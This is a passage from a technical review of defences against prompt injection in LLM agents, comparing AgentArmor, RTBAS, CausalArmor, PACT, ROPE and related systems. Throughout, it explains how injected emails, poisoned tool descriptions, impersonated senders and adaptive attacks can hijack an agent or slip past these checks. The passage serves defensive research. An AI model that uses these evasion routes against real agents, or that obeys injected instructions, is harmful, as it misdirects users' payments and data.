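An attacker can also try to cause errors deliberately. Wang and colleagues claim that AgentArmor is insensitive to adaptive attacks, which are designed with knowledge of the defence, but their appendix contradicts this. There they compare four ways of inferring dependencies and rate the language-model judge, which AgentArmor uses, as *not* resisting adaptive attacks. They chose it because it was the only method they rated as able to handle special cases such as conditional and transfer execution. They also concede in their limitations section that the analyser's reasoning may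 be wrong and that attackers might bypass it.

The analyser may itself be vulnerable to prompt injection, because it reads the same observations as the agent, including any injected text. It also reads the agent's thought, which may come from a model that the attacker has already hijacked. Wang and colleagues use a separate template to judge, after a run, whether an attack succeeded. That template includes a warning not to be misled by the injected text, but the analyser's template doesn't. The nine styles of attack in their tests are standard ones that target the agent, so the results don't show how well the analyser would resist text written to attack it.

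Attacking both models is harder than attacking the agent alone, because the same text must make the agent act and make the analyser attribute the action to something else. A model from 2026 would presumably also be a better analyser than those available in 2025. But AgentArmor's rules are only as reliable as the edges they check, and those edges depend on a language model interpreting hostile text correctly. The system as a whole is therefore not "insensitive to adaptive attacks", though its rules might be.

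### RTBAS

A system can limit the damage from a missed dependency by removing the overlooked text before the agent acts. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025), developed at Carnegie Mellon University, takes this approach. It divides the context into regions, each with its own security label. Before the agent's next step, a dependency screener selects the regions that seem relevant, and RTBAS joins their labels. It then redacts every region whose label isn't at or below the joined label. The model generates its call from what remains. If the joined label violates the policy for that call, RTBAS asks the user to confirm the call.

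If the RTBAS screener wrongly treats the malicious email as irrelevant, the joined label is trusted, so RTBAS removes the email before the model generates its next call. The injection then has no effect. In AgentArmor, the model has already generated the call after reading the email, and a missed edge hides the email's influence. Provided the labels are right, a mistake by the RTBAS screener reduces utility but not security. The agent may lack information it needs, or the user may have to confirm a harmless call. An attacker who misled the screener could still make the agent fail at its task.

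Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a language model that reads the context with each region marked and picks out the relevant ones. The other uses attention, the mechanism by which a model weighs earlier tokens as it computes a new one. For each input token *i* and output token *o*, it calculates an importance score:

A(i, o) ≈ Σₕ,ₗ | a(h, l, i, o) · ∂ℒ/∂a(h, l, i, o) |

Here *a* is the attention that one unit of the model, head *h* in layer *l*, gives to token *i* when computing token *o*. The loss ℒ measures how poorly the model predicted *o*. The sum approximates how much the loss would change if token *i* were masked.

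Providers of commercial models don't reveal attention weights, so Zhong and colleagues ran the same text through small open models. In one study, they examined 3,424 pairs of inputs and tool calls using a model with only 125 million parameters, and scaled each attention score against the highest in the context. For pairs with no dependency, 74% to 86% of scores were below 0.2. For pairs with a dependency, 14% were below 0.2 in GPT-4o's runs and 44% in Claude's. The scores help distinguish the two kinds of pairs, but a cut-off at 0.2 would have missed many dependencies in Claude's runs.

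The screener therefore summarises each region's scores as a sum, a mean and four quantiles, and passes these to a small recurrent neural network that labels the region relevant or not. The network was trained on data from 40 AgentDojo cases and was right 81% of the time on test data. If its errors were independent, it would get ten judgements in a row right only about 12% of the time. The screener would be a poor basis for security without the redaction step.

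On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the agent, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. The policy did not cover one attack in the office suite because it was in text written by the user, which was labeled as trusted. Under attack, utility fell by 2%, the figure reported in the abstract. Without attacks, it fell by 10% with the language-model screener and by 7.4% with the attention screener. In the Slack suite, it fell to 22% and 33% respectively, as many Slack tasks require the agent to act on text from untrusted websites. The test skipped any call that violated the policy, so asking users to confirm these calls instead could recover some of this loss. The language-model screener also roughly doubled the time and tokens used per banking task, from 4.4 to 9.7 seconds and from about 2,700 to 5,900 tokens.

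Zhong and colleagues also tested the screeners' judgements directly. They wrote 37 tasks involving private data and checked whether each screener identified exactly the categories of data that had affected a call. The language-model screener did so 70% of the time and the attention screener 57%. Simply assuming that every call depends on all the private data in view gave the exact answer 56.7% of the time, so on this measure attention added almost nothing. Wang and colleagues nevertheless rate attention-based methods as highly accurate and resistant to adaptive attacks, and they give no measurements for either rating. (Their appendix also credits these attention features to Siddiqui and colleagues, and the methods of Siddiqui and colleagues to RTBAS.)

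### Permissive label propagation

*Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) had already proposed running the model again on less text. Its method tests whether the model could have produced much the same output from less restricted inputs. In one example, a user asks how many people live in New York City, and a web search returns a trusted and an untrusted page that both contain a suitable figure. The trusted page is sufficient even if both pages influenced the original answer, so the system can answer again from that page alone and label the new answer as trusted.

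Let *x* be the prompt, *C* the documents in the context, *L* their joined label and *y* the model's output. For a more permissive label *L′*, let *C′* contain only the documents whose labels are at or below *L′*. Siddiqui and colleagues call *L′* λ-similar to *L* if

U(y | x, C) − U(y | x, C′) ≤ λ

The utility *U* is the negative of perplexity, a standard measure of how poorly a model predicts a text:

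U(y | x, C) = −(∏ᵢ p(yᵢ | x, C, y₁…yᵢ₋₁))^(−1/|y|)

The tolerance λ is the largest acceptable drop in utility. The algorithm starts with the label of the full context and tests the labels just below it. It continues downwards from each label that passes, and stops when none of the more permissive labels pass. With only two labels, trusted and untrusted, there is one alternative to test. In the worst case, when many documents have labels that can't be ranked, the number of tests grows exponentially.

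This test would separate the two payment cases well. If the user asked only for Alex's emails, removing the malicious email makes the payment call very improbable, so the call's label stays untrusted. If the user specified the payment, removing the emails should hardly affect the call. As in RTBAS, safety comes from the last step, in which the system runs the model again on *C′* and discards the original output. Even if the search makes errors, the new output depends only on documents at or below its label.

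Siddiqui and colleagues tested the search on synthetic questions whose answers were spread across 14 documents, each with its own label, which gives 2¹⁴ (16,384) possible combinations. The search found exactly the right set of labels for 86% of the questions with both the 7-billion and the 70-billion-parameter versions of Llama 2. Real news articles were harder. When a better label was possible, the search assigned one in 57% of cases with the smaller model and 39% with the larger. On a small set of agent conversations, it assigned a more permissive label than the baseline in more than 85% of cases. The results depended heavily on the choice of λ.

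They also tried a faster variant, which uses a kNN language model. This kind of model combines a prediction based on retrieved documents with one that ignores them:

p(y | x, C) = γ · p_kNN(y | x, C) + (1 − γ) · p_LM(y | x)

The part that depends on the documents takes little work to recompute, so the variant needs only one extra language model call per query. But it found the exact labels for only 53% to 58% of the synthetic questions.

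As a baseline, Siddiqui and colleagues asked the model itself which documents had influenced the output, much as AgentArmor does with its analyser. The smaller model gave exactly the right answer for 1.6% of the questions, and the larger for 12.7%. These figures are probably a poor guide to current models, because Llama 2 dates from 2023, accuracy rose steeply with size, and a newer language model did better than attention in the RTBAS tests. But they show that a model can produce fluent text without being able to identify its sources.

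### Leave-one-out attribution

Kim, Parmar and colleagues (2026), in *CausalArmor*, built their defence at Google and Seoul National University around the actual moment of danger. CausalArmor runs only when the agent proposes a privileged action, such as sending a message or writing a file. It removes one part of the context at a time and measures how much less probable the action becomes. For a part *X* of the context *C* and a proposed action *Y*, the score is

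Δ_X = log P(Y | C) − log P(Y | C without X)

CausalArmor divides each score by the number of tokens in *Y*, so that long and short calls are comparable. It then flags an untrusted part *S* if its score is greater than the user request's score minus a margin τ. At the default of τ = 0, it flags any untrusted text that supported the action more than the user's request did. With a larger τ, it flags more text.

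Suppose a hijacked agent proposes a payment with probability 0.8 (the numbers in this example are invented). The probability drops only to 0.7 if the user's request is removed, but to 0.001 if the malicious email is removed. Before adjusting for length, the scores are about 0.13 for the user's request and 6.7 for the email, so CausalArmor flags the email.

At this point, CausalArmor uses a second language model to remove instructions from the flagged text while trying to keep the facts, and replaces the agent's later reasoning with a placeholder. It then lets the agent choose its action again instead of blocking it. CausalArmor hides the reasoning because a hijacked agent may already have written down a justification for the attacker's action. Across all the tests, the average attack success rate was 0.29% with the reasoning hidden and 1.75% without hiding it. Such justifications are also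 a reason for caution about AgentArmor's analyser, which uses the agent's reasoning as evidence of what caused a call.

Cleaning the flagged input also makes false alarms less harmful. When an agent sends a reminder to addresses it has looked up, removing the lookup would make that exact call much less probable, even though the user asked for the reminder. The score doesn't distinguish control dependencies from data dependencies, so CausalArmor might flag the lookup. If the cleaning step works, it leaves the addresses in place and the agent still sends the reminder.

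Since commercial services often don't provide the necessary probabilities, Kim and colleagues calculate them with a smaller open model, Gemma 3 with 12 billion parameters. They tested the system on DoomArena, a benchmark in which an attacking model reads the conversation and adapts its injections to it. The agent, Gemini 3 Pro, handled 115 retail tasks:

| Defence | Tasks completed without attack | Attack success rate | Relative time without attack |
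|---|---|---|---|
| None | 73.6% | 88.9% | 1.00 |
| Repeating the user's request | 65.0% | 72.7% | 1.06 |
| PiGuard, a trained injection detector | 55.1% | 5.6% | 1.16 |
| CausalArmor | 71.0% | 3.7% | 1.38 |

These are strong results against an adaptive attacker, although as far as the description shows, the attacker adapts to the conversation and not to CausalArmor's scores. Kim and colleagues warn that an attacker could spread an injection over several parts of the context, or could optimise against the small model that calculates the scores if they knew which model it was. Removing one part at a time is weak against a spread-out injection. If two emails contain the same instruction, removing either one leaves the other in place, so both may receive low scores. Siddiqui and colleagues' method avoids this problem by removing all the untrusted documents together.

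Kim and colleagues also derive an upper bound on the probability that a run of *T* steps executes any of *m* harmful actions:

P(attack succeeds) ≤ T · m · e^(−(β + γ))

Here β measures how strongly the agent prefers the user's action when no untrusted text is present, and γ measures how far the cleaned text favours that action over a harmful one. With ten steps and five harmful actions, the bound falls below 1% only when β + γ exceeds about 8.5. The proof assumes both quantities are positive, which means it assumes the cleaning has worked. Kim and colleagues show that cleaning restores the influence of the user's request, but they don't measure γ for every harmful action. The bound explains why the defence could work but doesn't guarantee that it will.

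### Provenance for each argument

CausalArmor scores a call as a whole, whereas AgentArmor records separate sources for the tool and each parameter. In *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) credits a system called PACT with showing that a single trust label for a whole call is too coarse. Santos-Grueiro says that tracking the provenance of each argument can recover lost utility while still keeping untrusted text away from the arguments that matter.

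Santos-Grueiro's system, CXI, keeps a set of influences for each protected field in a call and another for the decision to make the call. The second set also covers whether the agent repeats, schedules or reorders the call. CXI treats the choice of a tool as untrusted if an untrusted message led the agent to make it, even if the tool's name comes from a trusted list. CXI rejects the call if the provenance of a protected field is unknown or ambiguous.

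Such a strict rule would block a lot of useful work if there were no way to accept values from untrusted text. CXI therefore permits a *typed release*, in which trusted code checks a value and approves it for one field. For example, an agent may need the log from an automated software test to identify the file it should repair, even though the log may be open to tampering. Trusted code can check that the file's path is valid and release it to the path field. The log's contents still can't determine which tool the agent uses, whether the change is approved or what command runs.

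In 400 coding runs, CXI completed 231 tasks safely, and Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorised field, effect or call getting past its checks. But the design assumes that the record captures every influence on a protected field, and Santos-Grueiro doesn't claim to establish noninterference inside the model. Typed releases make false edges less disruptive, because an edge from untrusted text no longer has to block a call if the value has passed a suitable check. They don't help when an edge is missed, because the system then has no reason to check the value.

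## Labelling tools and data

A dependency graph can trace a payment back to an email, but not show how far to trust the email or how secret its contents are. AgentArmor gets both from its property registry, which has one part for tools and one for data. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts security labels among the components that must be correct for a system's guarantees to hold. A wrong label affects every call that touches the mislabelled tool or file until someone corrects it, whereas a wrong edge in the graph usually affects one call.

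### The tool registry and `git_clone`

Each entry in the tool registry lists a tool's parameters, return values, side-effect inputs and side-effect outputs. Side-effect inputs are data the tool uses that doesn't appear in the trace, and side-effect outputs are data it creates but doesn't print. Every input and output has a data type, a role and expected security labels. A small data-flow graph records how data moves between them inside the tool.

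Wang and colleagues illustrate this with `git_clone`, the tool that clones a code repository. Its entry lists the web address as a parameter, `repo_url`, and the new folder that the trace never shows as a side-effect output, `local_repo`. The entry's graph has an arrow from `repo_url` to `local_repo`, and the folder inherits its labels along that arrow. (The printed description has `local_repo` inheriting from itself, evidently a slip for `repo_url`.)

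A repository's address and its contents need separate labels. A user may have typed the address, which makes it trustworthy, while a stranger wrote the code. If the contents inherited the address's label, an injection in the repository's README would look like the user's own words. AgentArmor's automatic labeller therefore determines whether a parameter holds data or only refers to it, and whether the tool reads or writes the data it refers to.

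### Levels, defaults and sources

The data registry has an entry for each file path, URL, temporary folder or similar item. The entry gives the item a kind, such as `local_folder` or `remote_api`, and labels for confidentiality and integrity. Both labels have three levels: low, mid and high. The default labels are:

| Element | Integrity | Confidentiality |
|---|---|---|
| Tool name | High | High |
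| Tool parameter | High | Mid |
| Tool's return value | Low | Mid |
| Data | Low | Mid |

The labels on names and parameters make most sense as limits on what may influence or enter a call, while those on return values and data describe where something came from. A second set of rules assigns labels according to the tool's source. Names and parameters have high integrity in every case, and the other labels vary:

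| Source of the tool | Risks listed | Confidentiality of name and parameters | Integrity of result | Confidentiality of result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| External public | Prompt injection, tool poisoning, data leakage | Mid | Low | Low |
| External official | Prompt injection, tool poisoning, data leakage | Mid | Mid | Low |
| Internal public | Prompt injection, dangerous behaviour, data leakage | High | Mid | High |
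| Internal trusted | Prompt injection, dangerous behaviour | High | High | High |

The default labels are much stricter about trust than about secrecy. An unlabelled file has low integrity, so an injection inside it gains no authority. But the file has mid confidentiality, the highest level allowed in the parameters of an external public tool, so an agent could send any unlabelled file to a public web service unless a separate rule forbids it. Protection against leaks depends on a person or a scanner first marking sensitive files as high confidentiality.

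The defaults also make the `git_clone` entry less important, since an unregistered README would have low integrity anyway. The entry matters most when the operator has marked the agent's working folder as trusted, or when the repository is private and the local copy must inherit its high confidentiality.

The source-based rules have a different weakness, because a tool's supplier didn't necessarily write what the tool returns. A company's own email tool would presumably count as internal trusted, which gives its results high integrity, yet it returns messages from strangers. In the example of the payment to Alex, AgentArmor avoids this mistake because the registry separately lists the stored emails as low-integrity data, and the join passes that label on to the observation. If the tool's entry left out the stored emails, the malicious message could be labelled high-integrity.

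*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) marks the results of unlabelled tools as unknown instead of guessing a level. Unknown sits outside the scale from suspicious to trusted. The agent can keep using the data, and the system needs a real label only when the data reaches a call with a security requirement. An approved converter then assigns one, up to a ceiling set in advance. If no converter applies, the system blocks the call. The ceiling limits the damage from a bad classifier. With a ceiling of mid integrity, for instance, a classifier fooled by an attacker could not give a stranger's web page high integrity.

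### Filling the registry automatically

Wang and colleagues acknowledge that writing entries by hand for many tools is slow and error-prone, so AgentArmor has three ways to fill the registry. A static labeller converts an operator's manual settings into the registry's format. An automatic labeller analyses tool descriptions and available data before deployment. A runtime labeller automatically handles tools and data that first appear during a run.

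For each tool, the automatic labeller extracts the parameters and analyses the data flow through them to determine which ones the return value depends on. It then assesses the tool's risk based on its source and whether it reads or writes. The risk of leaks affects the confidentiality of the parameters, and the potential for dangerous behaviour affects integrity. For data, the labeller checks the format and origin and scans the contents for sensitive information.

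The runtime labeller looks for new tools in the system prompt, where their descriptions normally appear, and uses a language model to write an entry for each. It also checks the descriptions for injected instructions and scans observations for sensitive information. For example, this scan might find a password in an otherwise ordinary file and raise the file's confidentiality, even though the file's location and the tool's source would not justify this on their own.

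### Hostile and outdated descriptions

A tool's supplier usually writes its description, and the supplier may be an attacker. Many agents get tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard from late 2024 that lets outside servers offer tools. *MCPTox* (2025), a benchmark built on real MCP servers, tests tool poisoning, in which the attacker hides instructions in a tool's description. The model reads these instructions when the tool is registered, before calling any tool.

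A poisoned tool description could cause AgentArmor's labelling model to assign high integrity to the tool's results. It could also influence the agent directly from the system prompt, which AgentArmor's worked example labels as high integrity. A call that followed an instruction in the description might then look as if the developer had authorised it. The runtime labeller's check for injections offers some protection, but attackers can adapt to detectors of this kind. The threat model assumes that tools behave as specified, even though the source-based rules list tool poisoning as a risk for every external tool.

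Labels can also become outdated. MCP has no way to pin a description to a version, as *MCPThreatHive* (2026) points out, so a server may pass an audit and behave differently later. An operator could store a fingerprint of each description and relabel the tool whenever it changed, but this would not detect a change in the tool's code. Invisible characters in a description can also hide instructions from a human reviewer.

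*ETDI* (2025) proposes tying tool definitions to OAuth, a standard for authorising access between services, so that an agent's software can verify a tool's identity. This would make it harder to pass off a public tool as an official one. But *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* stresses that authentication establishes where a tool comes from, not whether it is safe, and a genuine tool can still return a malicious web page.

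An operator can also test whether a tool behaves as described. *My Credentials, Please* (2026) presents MCP-FSD, which infers from a tool's description and configuration which files the tool should access. MCP-FSD then runs the tool with malicious arguments, and with harmless ones as a control, to see whether the tool exposes planted credentials. A labeller that only reads descriptions can't detect this behaviour.

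*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (2026) proposes that MCP servers supply the confidentiality and trust labels themselves. MCP currently offers only a few optional annotations and advises treating tools as untrusted. Server-supplied labels could work within a company, where the operator can trust whoever wrote them. In an open market, a malicious server could declare its output trustworthy, so the operator would need to restrict agents to trusted vendors or require independent certification.

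### One label for a whole inbox

In the payment example, a single data item, `email_data`, represents all the stored emails and has low integrity and mid confidentiality. Low integrity suits a stranger's message, but the same label applies to an invoice from the user's accountant, so a rule that protects payments might block the user from paying it. Mid confidentiality is probably too strict for a newsletter and too lax for a payslip.

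The operator could label emails by sender instead, provided the mail system authenticates the sender's address. AgentArmor would also need a separate node for each message, because an email search may return several messages in one observation, and the analyser attributes a call to the observation as a whole. If the accountant's message and a stranger's message share a node, the join makes both untrusted. Even with separate nodes, a stranger's text would get the accountant's label if the accountant quoted it.

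*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats how finely to label as an open problem, because the tokens a model reads have no natural boundaries between sources. It suggests using existing boundaries, such as those between messages, or labelling web text by the site it came from. *AgentKernel* (2026) labels individual items in an agent's memory and acknowledges the tradeoff. One label for a whole session is sound but causes label creep. Labels for single items are far more usable, but an attacker can get an item too permissive a label by misleading the step that matches items to their sources. AgentKernel therefore also restricts tools at the operating-system level.

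The levels themselves can be too coarse. Suppose a company has a salary file for its personnel staff and a contract for its lawyers. Both would have high confidentiality, so the levels alone wouldn't stop the agent from sending the salaries to the lawyers. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* describes labels that instead list the authorised readers. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one document and Ben, Cara and Dan another, only Ben and Cara may read a text that draws on both:

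{Ann, Ben, Cara} ∩ {Ben, Cara, Dan} = {Ben, Cara}

Such labels are more precise, but someone has to keep the lists of readers up to date.

A single label for a tool has the same problem, because a file search, for example, can reach any folder depending on its parameters. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) therefore describes each call by where the data comes from, where it goes, how sensitive it is and what effects the call has. A rule can then allow reading from the local disk and forbid writing to an outside network, whichever tool the agent uses.

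### How accurate the labels are

Wang and colleagues report no accuracy figures for AgentArmor's labels, whether manual or automatic. The closest evidence comes from *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026), which presents SEAgent, another defence that checks labelled graphs of agent runs. OpenAI's o1 model and human annotators independently labelled 80 tools from InjecAgent, a benchmark of prompt injection. The paper measures their agreement with Cohen's kappa:

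κ = (pₒ − pₑ) / (1 − pₑ)

Here pₒ is the share of labels that matched and pₑ is the share expected to match by chance. A kappa of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means no more agreement than chance would produce.

| Attribute | Kappa |
|---|---|
| Object: local, external or physical | 1.00 |
| Action: read, write or execute | 0.89 |
| Sensitivity of the operation | 0.77 |
| Privacy of the result | 0.87 |
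| Integrity of the result | 0.92 |
| Overall | 0.95 |

The overall figure is higher than those for four of the five attributes, probably because pooling different attributes lowers the agreement expected by chance. Agreement was weakest on sensitivity, which determines how strictly SEAgent protects a tool. The model rated a tool that opens web pages as low, while the annotators rated it as moderate because it could lead a user to a phishing site. SEAgent's rule against indirect injection covers only tools of moderate or high sensitivity, so the model's label would have left this tool unprotected. SEAgent's developers therefore had people check and correct the model's labels. Both the model and the annotators worked from tool descriptions, so their agreement shows that they interpret the descriptions similarly, not that the labels match what the tools do.

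Some labels have no clearly correct value. SEAgent raised two false alarms in another test because the agent had consulted Wikipedia, which was labelled as unfiltered, before recording health data or booking an appointment. The paper suggests labelling Wikipedia as trusted in a real deployment. That would remove the false alarms, but it would also let an attacker's text influence those actions, because almost anyone can edit Wikipedia.

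Automated methods do fairly well on the related task of listing the permissions a tool needs. *AgentBound* (2025) compared generated lists with human-written ones for 48 MCP servers. The lists were identical for 28 servers and differed by one permission for 14, and the worst list lacked four. The paper scores a list with one difference as about 94% accurate, but an operator would still have to correct the lists for 20 servers.

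*Empowering Edge Agents* (2026) reports a small test of content scanning, in which a person checked 50 items that the language model GLM-5.3 had marked as sensitive and confirmed 45. Since the sample contained only marked items, it doesn't show how many sensitive items the model missed. In AgentArmor, missed items would be more dangerous than wrongly marked ones, because they would keep their mid confidentiality level and could leave through an external tool.

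People also make labelling mistakes. In *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (2026), a researcher labelled the permissions that various tasks required, then reviewed every disagreement with a language model's labels. Some of the disagreements came from the researcher's own errors. The same person did the labelling and the review, so the corrected labels may still contain misjudgements made in both steps.

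An operator also has to write the rules that use the labels. Evidence from ordinary software suggests developers find this difficult. In the code repositories that *Reparo* (2026) examined, between 40.6% and 55.7% of access-control policies failed the validation tool for their own language. Reparo uses a language model to write and repair policies, and 99% to 100% of its policies passed. A valid policy can still grant access to the wrong person, so Reparo also tests each one on sample requests with known correct answers. Those answers depend on the intended rules, which are often scattered across code, comments and documentation.

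## Assigning, propagating and checking security types

The property registry supplies labels for the sources of a run, such as the user's prompt and the stored emails. AgentArmor's type system carries those labels along the graph's edges to the pending tool call and decides whether the call may run. Its type assigner copies labels from the registry to nodes, its inference step computes labels for the remaining nodes, and its type checker looks for violations.

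### Security types and rule types

In a programming language, a type usually describes what kind of value something is, so that a checker can reject an attempt to multiply a number by a name. AgentArmor's types describe how far to trust a value and who may see it. Wang and colleagues define the type of each node as a pair:

Type = {security type, rule type}

The security type combines the node's confidentiality and integrity labels. The rule type is a logical condition that must hold before the call runs. It can refer to the node's own labels, to specific values, or to the type or state of another node. In one of the paper's examples, the agent may send a file's contents only if the recipient belongs to a privileged group. Another example requires a node to have high confidentiality if another parameter exceeds a threshold.

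### Propagating labels and checking edges

A node with one incoming edge inherits the label of its source, and a node with several takes the join of their labels. Let C(v) and I(v) be the confidentiality and integrity of node *v*, with low < mid < high, and let u → v stand for an edge from *u* to *v*. Then

C(v) = max C(u), over all u → v

I(v) = min I(u), over all u → v

In the payment example, this is how the stored emails' low integrity reaches the observation, even though the sender's name comes from the user.

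The type checker then examines every edge. For an edge from *u* to *v*, it requires

C(u) ≤ C(v) and I(u) ≥ I(v)

Confidentiality must not fall along an edge, and integrity must not rise.

However, a label computed by the join always passes this check, because the maximum of several levels is at least as high as each of them and the minimum is at least as low. If AgentArmor computed every label this way, every graph would pass the edge check, including the graph of a hijacked run.

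To find a violation, the checker needs a second label, independent of the sources, that limits what the node may accept. Suppose an agent puts the contents of a high-confidentiality payroll file into a parameter of a public web tool. The join gives the parameter high confidentiality, so the edge passes the check. If the parameter instead keeps the mid confidentiality that the registry assigns to such tools, the edge runs from high to mid and fails.

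Wang and colleagues don't explain which label applies when a node could have both a default label from the registry and one propagated from its sources. The registry gives every tool name and parameter high integrity by default. If those defaults were limits, any edge from a low-integrity observation would fail. But in the worked example, names and parameters take the integrity of their sources, and the defaults have no effect.

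Fan, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, keep the two labels apart in PACT, the system that Santos-Grueiro credits with showing the weakness of one trust label per call. PACT computes the trust of each value with much the same join. A separate contract for the tool sets the minimum trust for each argument, and the call runs only if

trust of the value ≥ minimum trust for the argument

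AgentArmor's rule types can play the same part as PACT's minimum, but only where someone has written a suitable rule.

### The payment to Alex

In the payment example, the user asked for emails from Alex, and one of those emails contained an instruction to pay him 10 dollars. The registry gives the system prompt and the user's prompt high integrity, the stored emails low integrity, and all three mid confidentiality. The inference step produces these labels:

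| Node | Source of its label | Integrity | Confidentiality |
|---|---|---|---|
| `search_email` (name) | User's prompt | High | Mid |
| `sender="Alex"` | User's prompt | High | Mid |
| Observation | `search_email` (tool) | Low | Mid |
| `create_trans` (name) | Observation | Low | Mid |
| `receiver="Alex"` | Observation | Low | Mid |
| `amount="10$"` | Observation | Low | Mid |

Every edge passes the check. The checker then evaluates the rule for `create_trans`, which blocks the call if

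(I(receiver) ≤ mid or I(amount) ≤ mid) and the agent's role is email-focused

Both parameters have low integrity, and the system prompt restricts the agent to email tools. The call therefore violates the rule, and AgentArmor aborts the payment before any money is sent.

AgentArmor has traced the choice of `create_trans` to a stranger's email, but this rule doesn't use that information. Suppose the user had asked for emails in which Alex requests 10 dollars. If an injection then caused the payment, the analyser might trace both the receiver and the amount to the user's prompt, and the rule would let the payment through. A rule of this form also can't block a tool that takes no parameters, such as one that clears the agent's memory.

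The condition about the agent's role limits the rule further. It is false for a banking agent, so the rule never blocks anything there, and the operator needs a different rule for the setting where payments matter most. The role appears only as a sentence in the system prompt, and Wang and colleagues don't explain how the checker turns that sentence into a condition it can test.

### The meeting reminder

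Emailing the reminder to a meeting attendee is a legitimate task with a similar graph. The user's request leads the agent to choose the email tool, and a lookup supplies the recipient's address.

Wang and colleagues use this task to explain dependencies and don't apply the type system to it, but the result is easy to work out. By default, a tool's result has low integrity, so the recipient has low integrity too, like the receiver of the injected payment. The calls differ in the label of the tool name, which is high for the reminder, because the user's request caused the choice of tool, and low for the payment.

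If the operator adapts the payment rule to require high integrity for every parameter of the email tool, the rule blocks the reminder. Tasks of this kind are common, at least in benchmarks. *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) sorts tasks by how much the user specifies. In 30 of the 60 tasks in AgentDyn, a benchmark where agents have to adjust their plans to what they find, the user names the action but leaves a value for the agent to find elsewhere. The same is true of 26 of the 57 tasks in three AgentDojo suites.

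When Fan and colleagues required every argument to be as trustworthy as the user's own words, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 14.4% of AgentDojo's tasks. They apparently ran this test on the weakest of their five models, which completed 20.6% with no defence, so the rule reduced the number of tasks it completed by about 30%.

The operator could instead check only the choice of tool. The reminder would then pass and the injected payment would fail, but an attacker could supply the reminder's address. A stranger might write in the meeting invitation that the attendee's email address has changed. The choice of the email tool would still come from the user's request, so the tool name would keep its high integrity and the reminder would go to the attacker.

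Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026) observed an attack of this kind in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, when they gave Claude Sonnet 5 ten difficult tasks containing injections, with Anthropic's safety classifiers switched on. Two of the attacks succeeded, both through an email from a sender whose address resembled a colleague's. The user had asked the agent to send the colleague a sales report, and the agent sent it to the impersonator. A check on the choice of action would not have caught this, because the user did ask the agent to send the report. Claude Opus 5 resisted all ten attacks.

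The legitimate reminder and the redirected one have identical labels, with high integrity for the tool name and low integrity for the recipient. Any rule that considers only these labels must therefore allow both or block both. To separate them, a rule needs to know more about where the address came from. It could, for instance, allow the reminder only if

I(tool name) = high and (recipient ∈ P or recipient ∈ A)

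Here P contains the addresses in the user's prompt, and A contains those in the attendee field of the meeting the user meant. The rule ignores addresses that appear only in the invitation's free text. The three rules give these results:

| Call | All parameters must be trusted | Choice of tool must be trusted | Rule with P and A |
|---|---|---|---|
| Requested reminder to an address in the attendee field | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed |
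| Requested reminder to an address planted in the invitation's text | Blocked | Allowed | Blocked |
| Email to an attendee that the user never requested | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

The third row shows why the rule has to include the choice of tool. Without that condition, an injection could make the agent send unwanted messages to everyone at the meeting.

An operator could probably express this rule in AgentArmor, since rule types can refer to values and to other nodes. But AgentArmor represents the whole lookup result as one observation, so the operator would first have to separate the attendee field from the text around it. The field must also be one that strangers can't edit, because an attacker who organised the meeting would also have chosen the attendees.

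### Rules for particular arguments and tasks

PACT makes rules more precise by giving each argument of a tool call a role. Recipients and web addresses are targets, message bodies are content, and other roles cover commands, credentials, selectors and control flags. Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to a named manager. The page has to determine the body of the email but should not affect the recipient. A single minimum trust level for the whole call would either block this task or let the page redirect the email, so PACT sets a low minimum for the body and a high one for the recipient.

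Fan and colleagues tested PACT on AgentDojo with several models. On the three strongest, no attack succeeded, and the agents completed 38.1% to 46.4% of the tasks, compared with 46.4% to 59.8% without a defence. The loss of utility is moderate, but the security result is weak evidence because only one to three of the 27 injections had succeeded against these models without a defence.

Even with roles, PACT would probably block the reminder unless some trusted procedure approved the attendee's address. The address is a target, so PACT requires high trust for it, but it comes from a tool, and PACT assigns tools less trust than the user.

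ROPE, the system that Ma and colleagues built, varies the rule with the task. Before the agent starts, a language model reads the user's request and other trusted information, and selects a rule for each sensitive parameter. It never reads the tool results that might contain an injection. Three of the available rules limit where a value may come from:

- the user's request;
- the request, or an authenticated source that the user named;
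- the request, or the user's own protected records.

Ordinary code then compares each proposed value with the text of the permitted sources. The third rule would work for the reminder if the calendar's attendee field counted as a protected record.

In one of the paper's examples, the user says that Lily has emailed a link to a shared document, and asks the agent to summarise the document and send her the summary. The request names Lily as a source, so ROPE accepts the address on her authenticated email. A stranger can write an email that claims to be from Lily, but the mail system stamps it with the stranger's own address, and ROPE doesn't accept values from it. ROPE also requires a complete match, so an attacker can't use a trusted text containing `notevil.com` to get `evil.com` accepted.

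Protected records are trustworthy only if the agent can't write untrusted data to them. For example, an injection might make the agent add a stranger to the attendee list, and a later reminder would then go to the stranger because the field appears protected. Ma and colleagues therefore check every value the agent writes to such a field against a rule at least as strict as the rules for later calls that use the field. PACT addresses the same danger by tracking a value's original sources through later tool calls. When Fan and colleagues removed this tracking in a controlled test, security fell from 100% to 80%.

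On the AgentDyn tasks where the agent must find a value the user didn't give, agents protected by ROPE completed 44.2% on average, with an attack success rate of 0.6%. The best of the other defences with low attack success completed 24.2%. Across all of AgentDyn, ROPE reduced the attack success rate against GPT-4o-mini from 49.6% to 0.3%, while the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 46.7% to 36.7%. These results are much better than one would expect from a uniform strict rule, though GPT-4o-mini is an old model and unusually easy to hijack.

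ROPE's guarantee covers where a value occurs but not whether it is the right one. Ma and colleagues point out that an injection can still steer the agent's choice among accepted values, so the reminder might go to the wrong attendee. It can also cause an inappropriate action that uses an accepted value. AgentArmor's control dependencies could help in the second case, because they would link the action to the injection.

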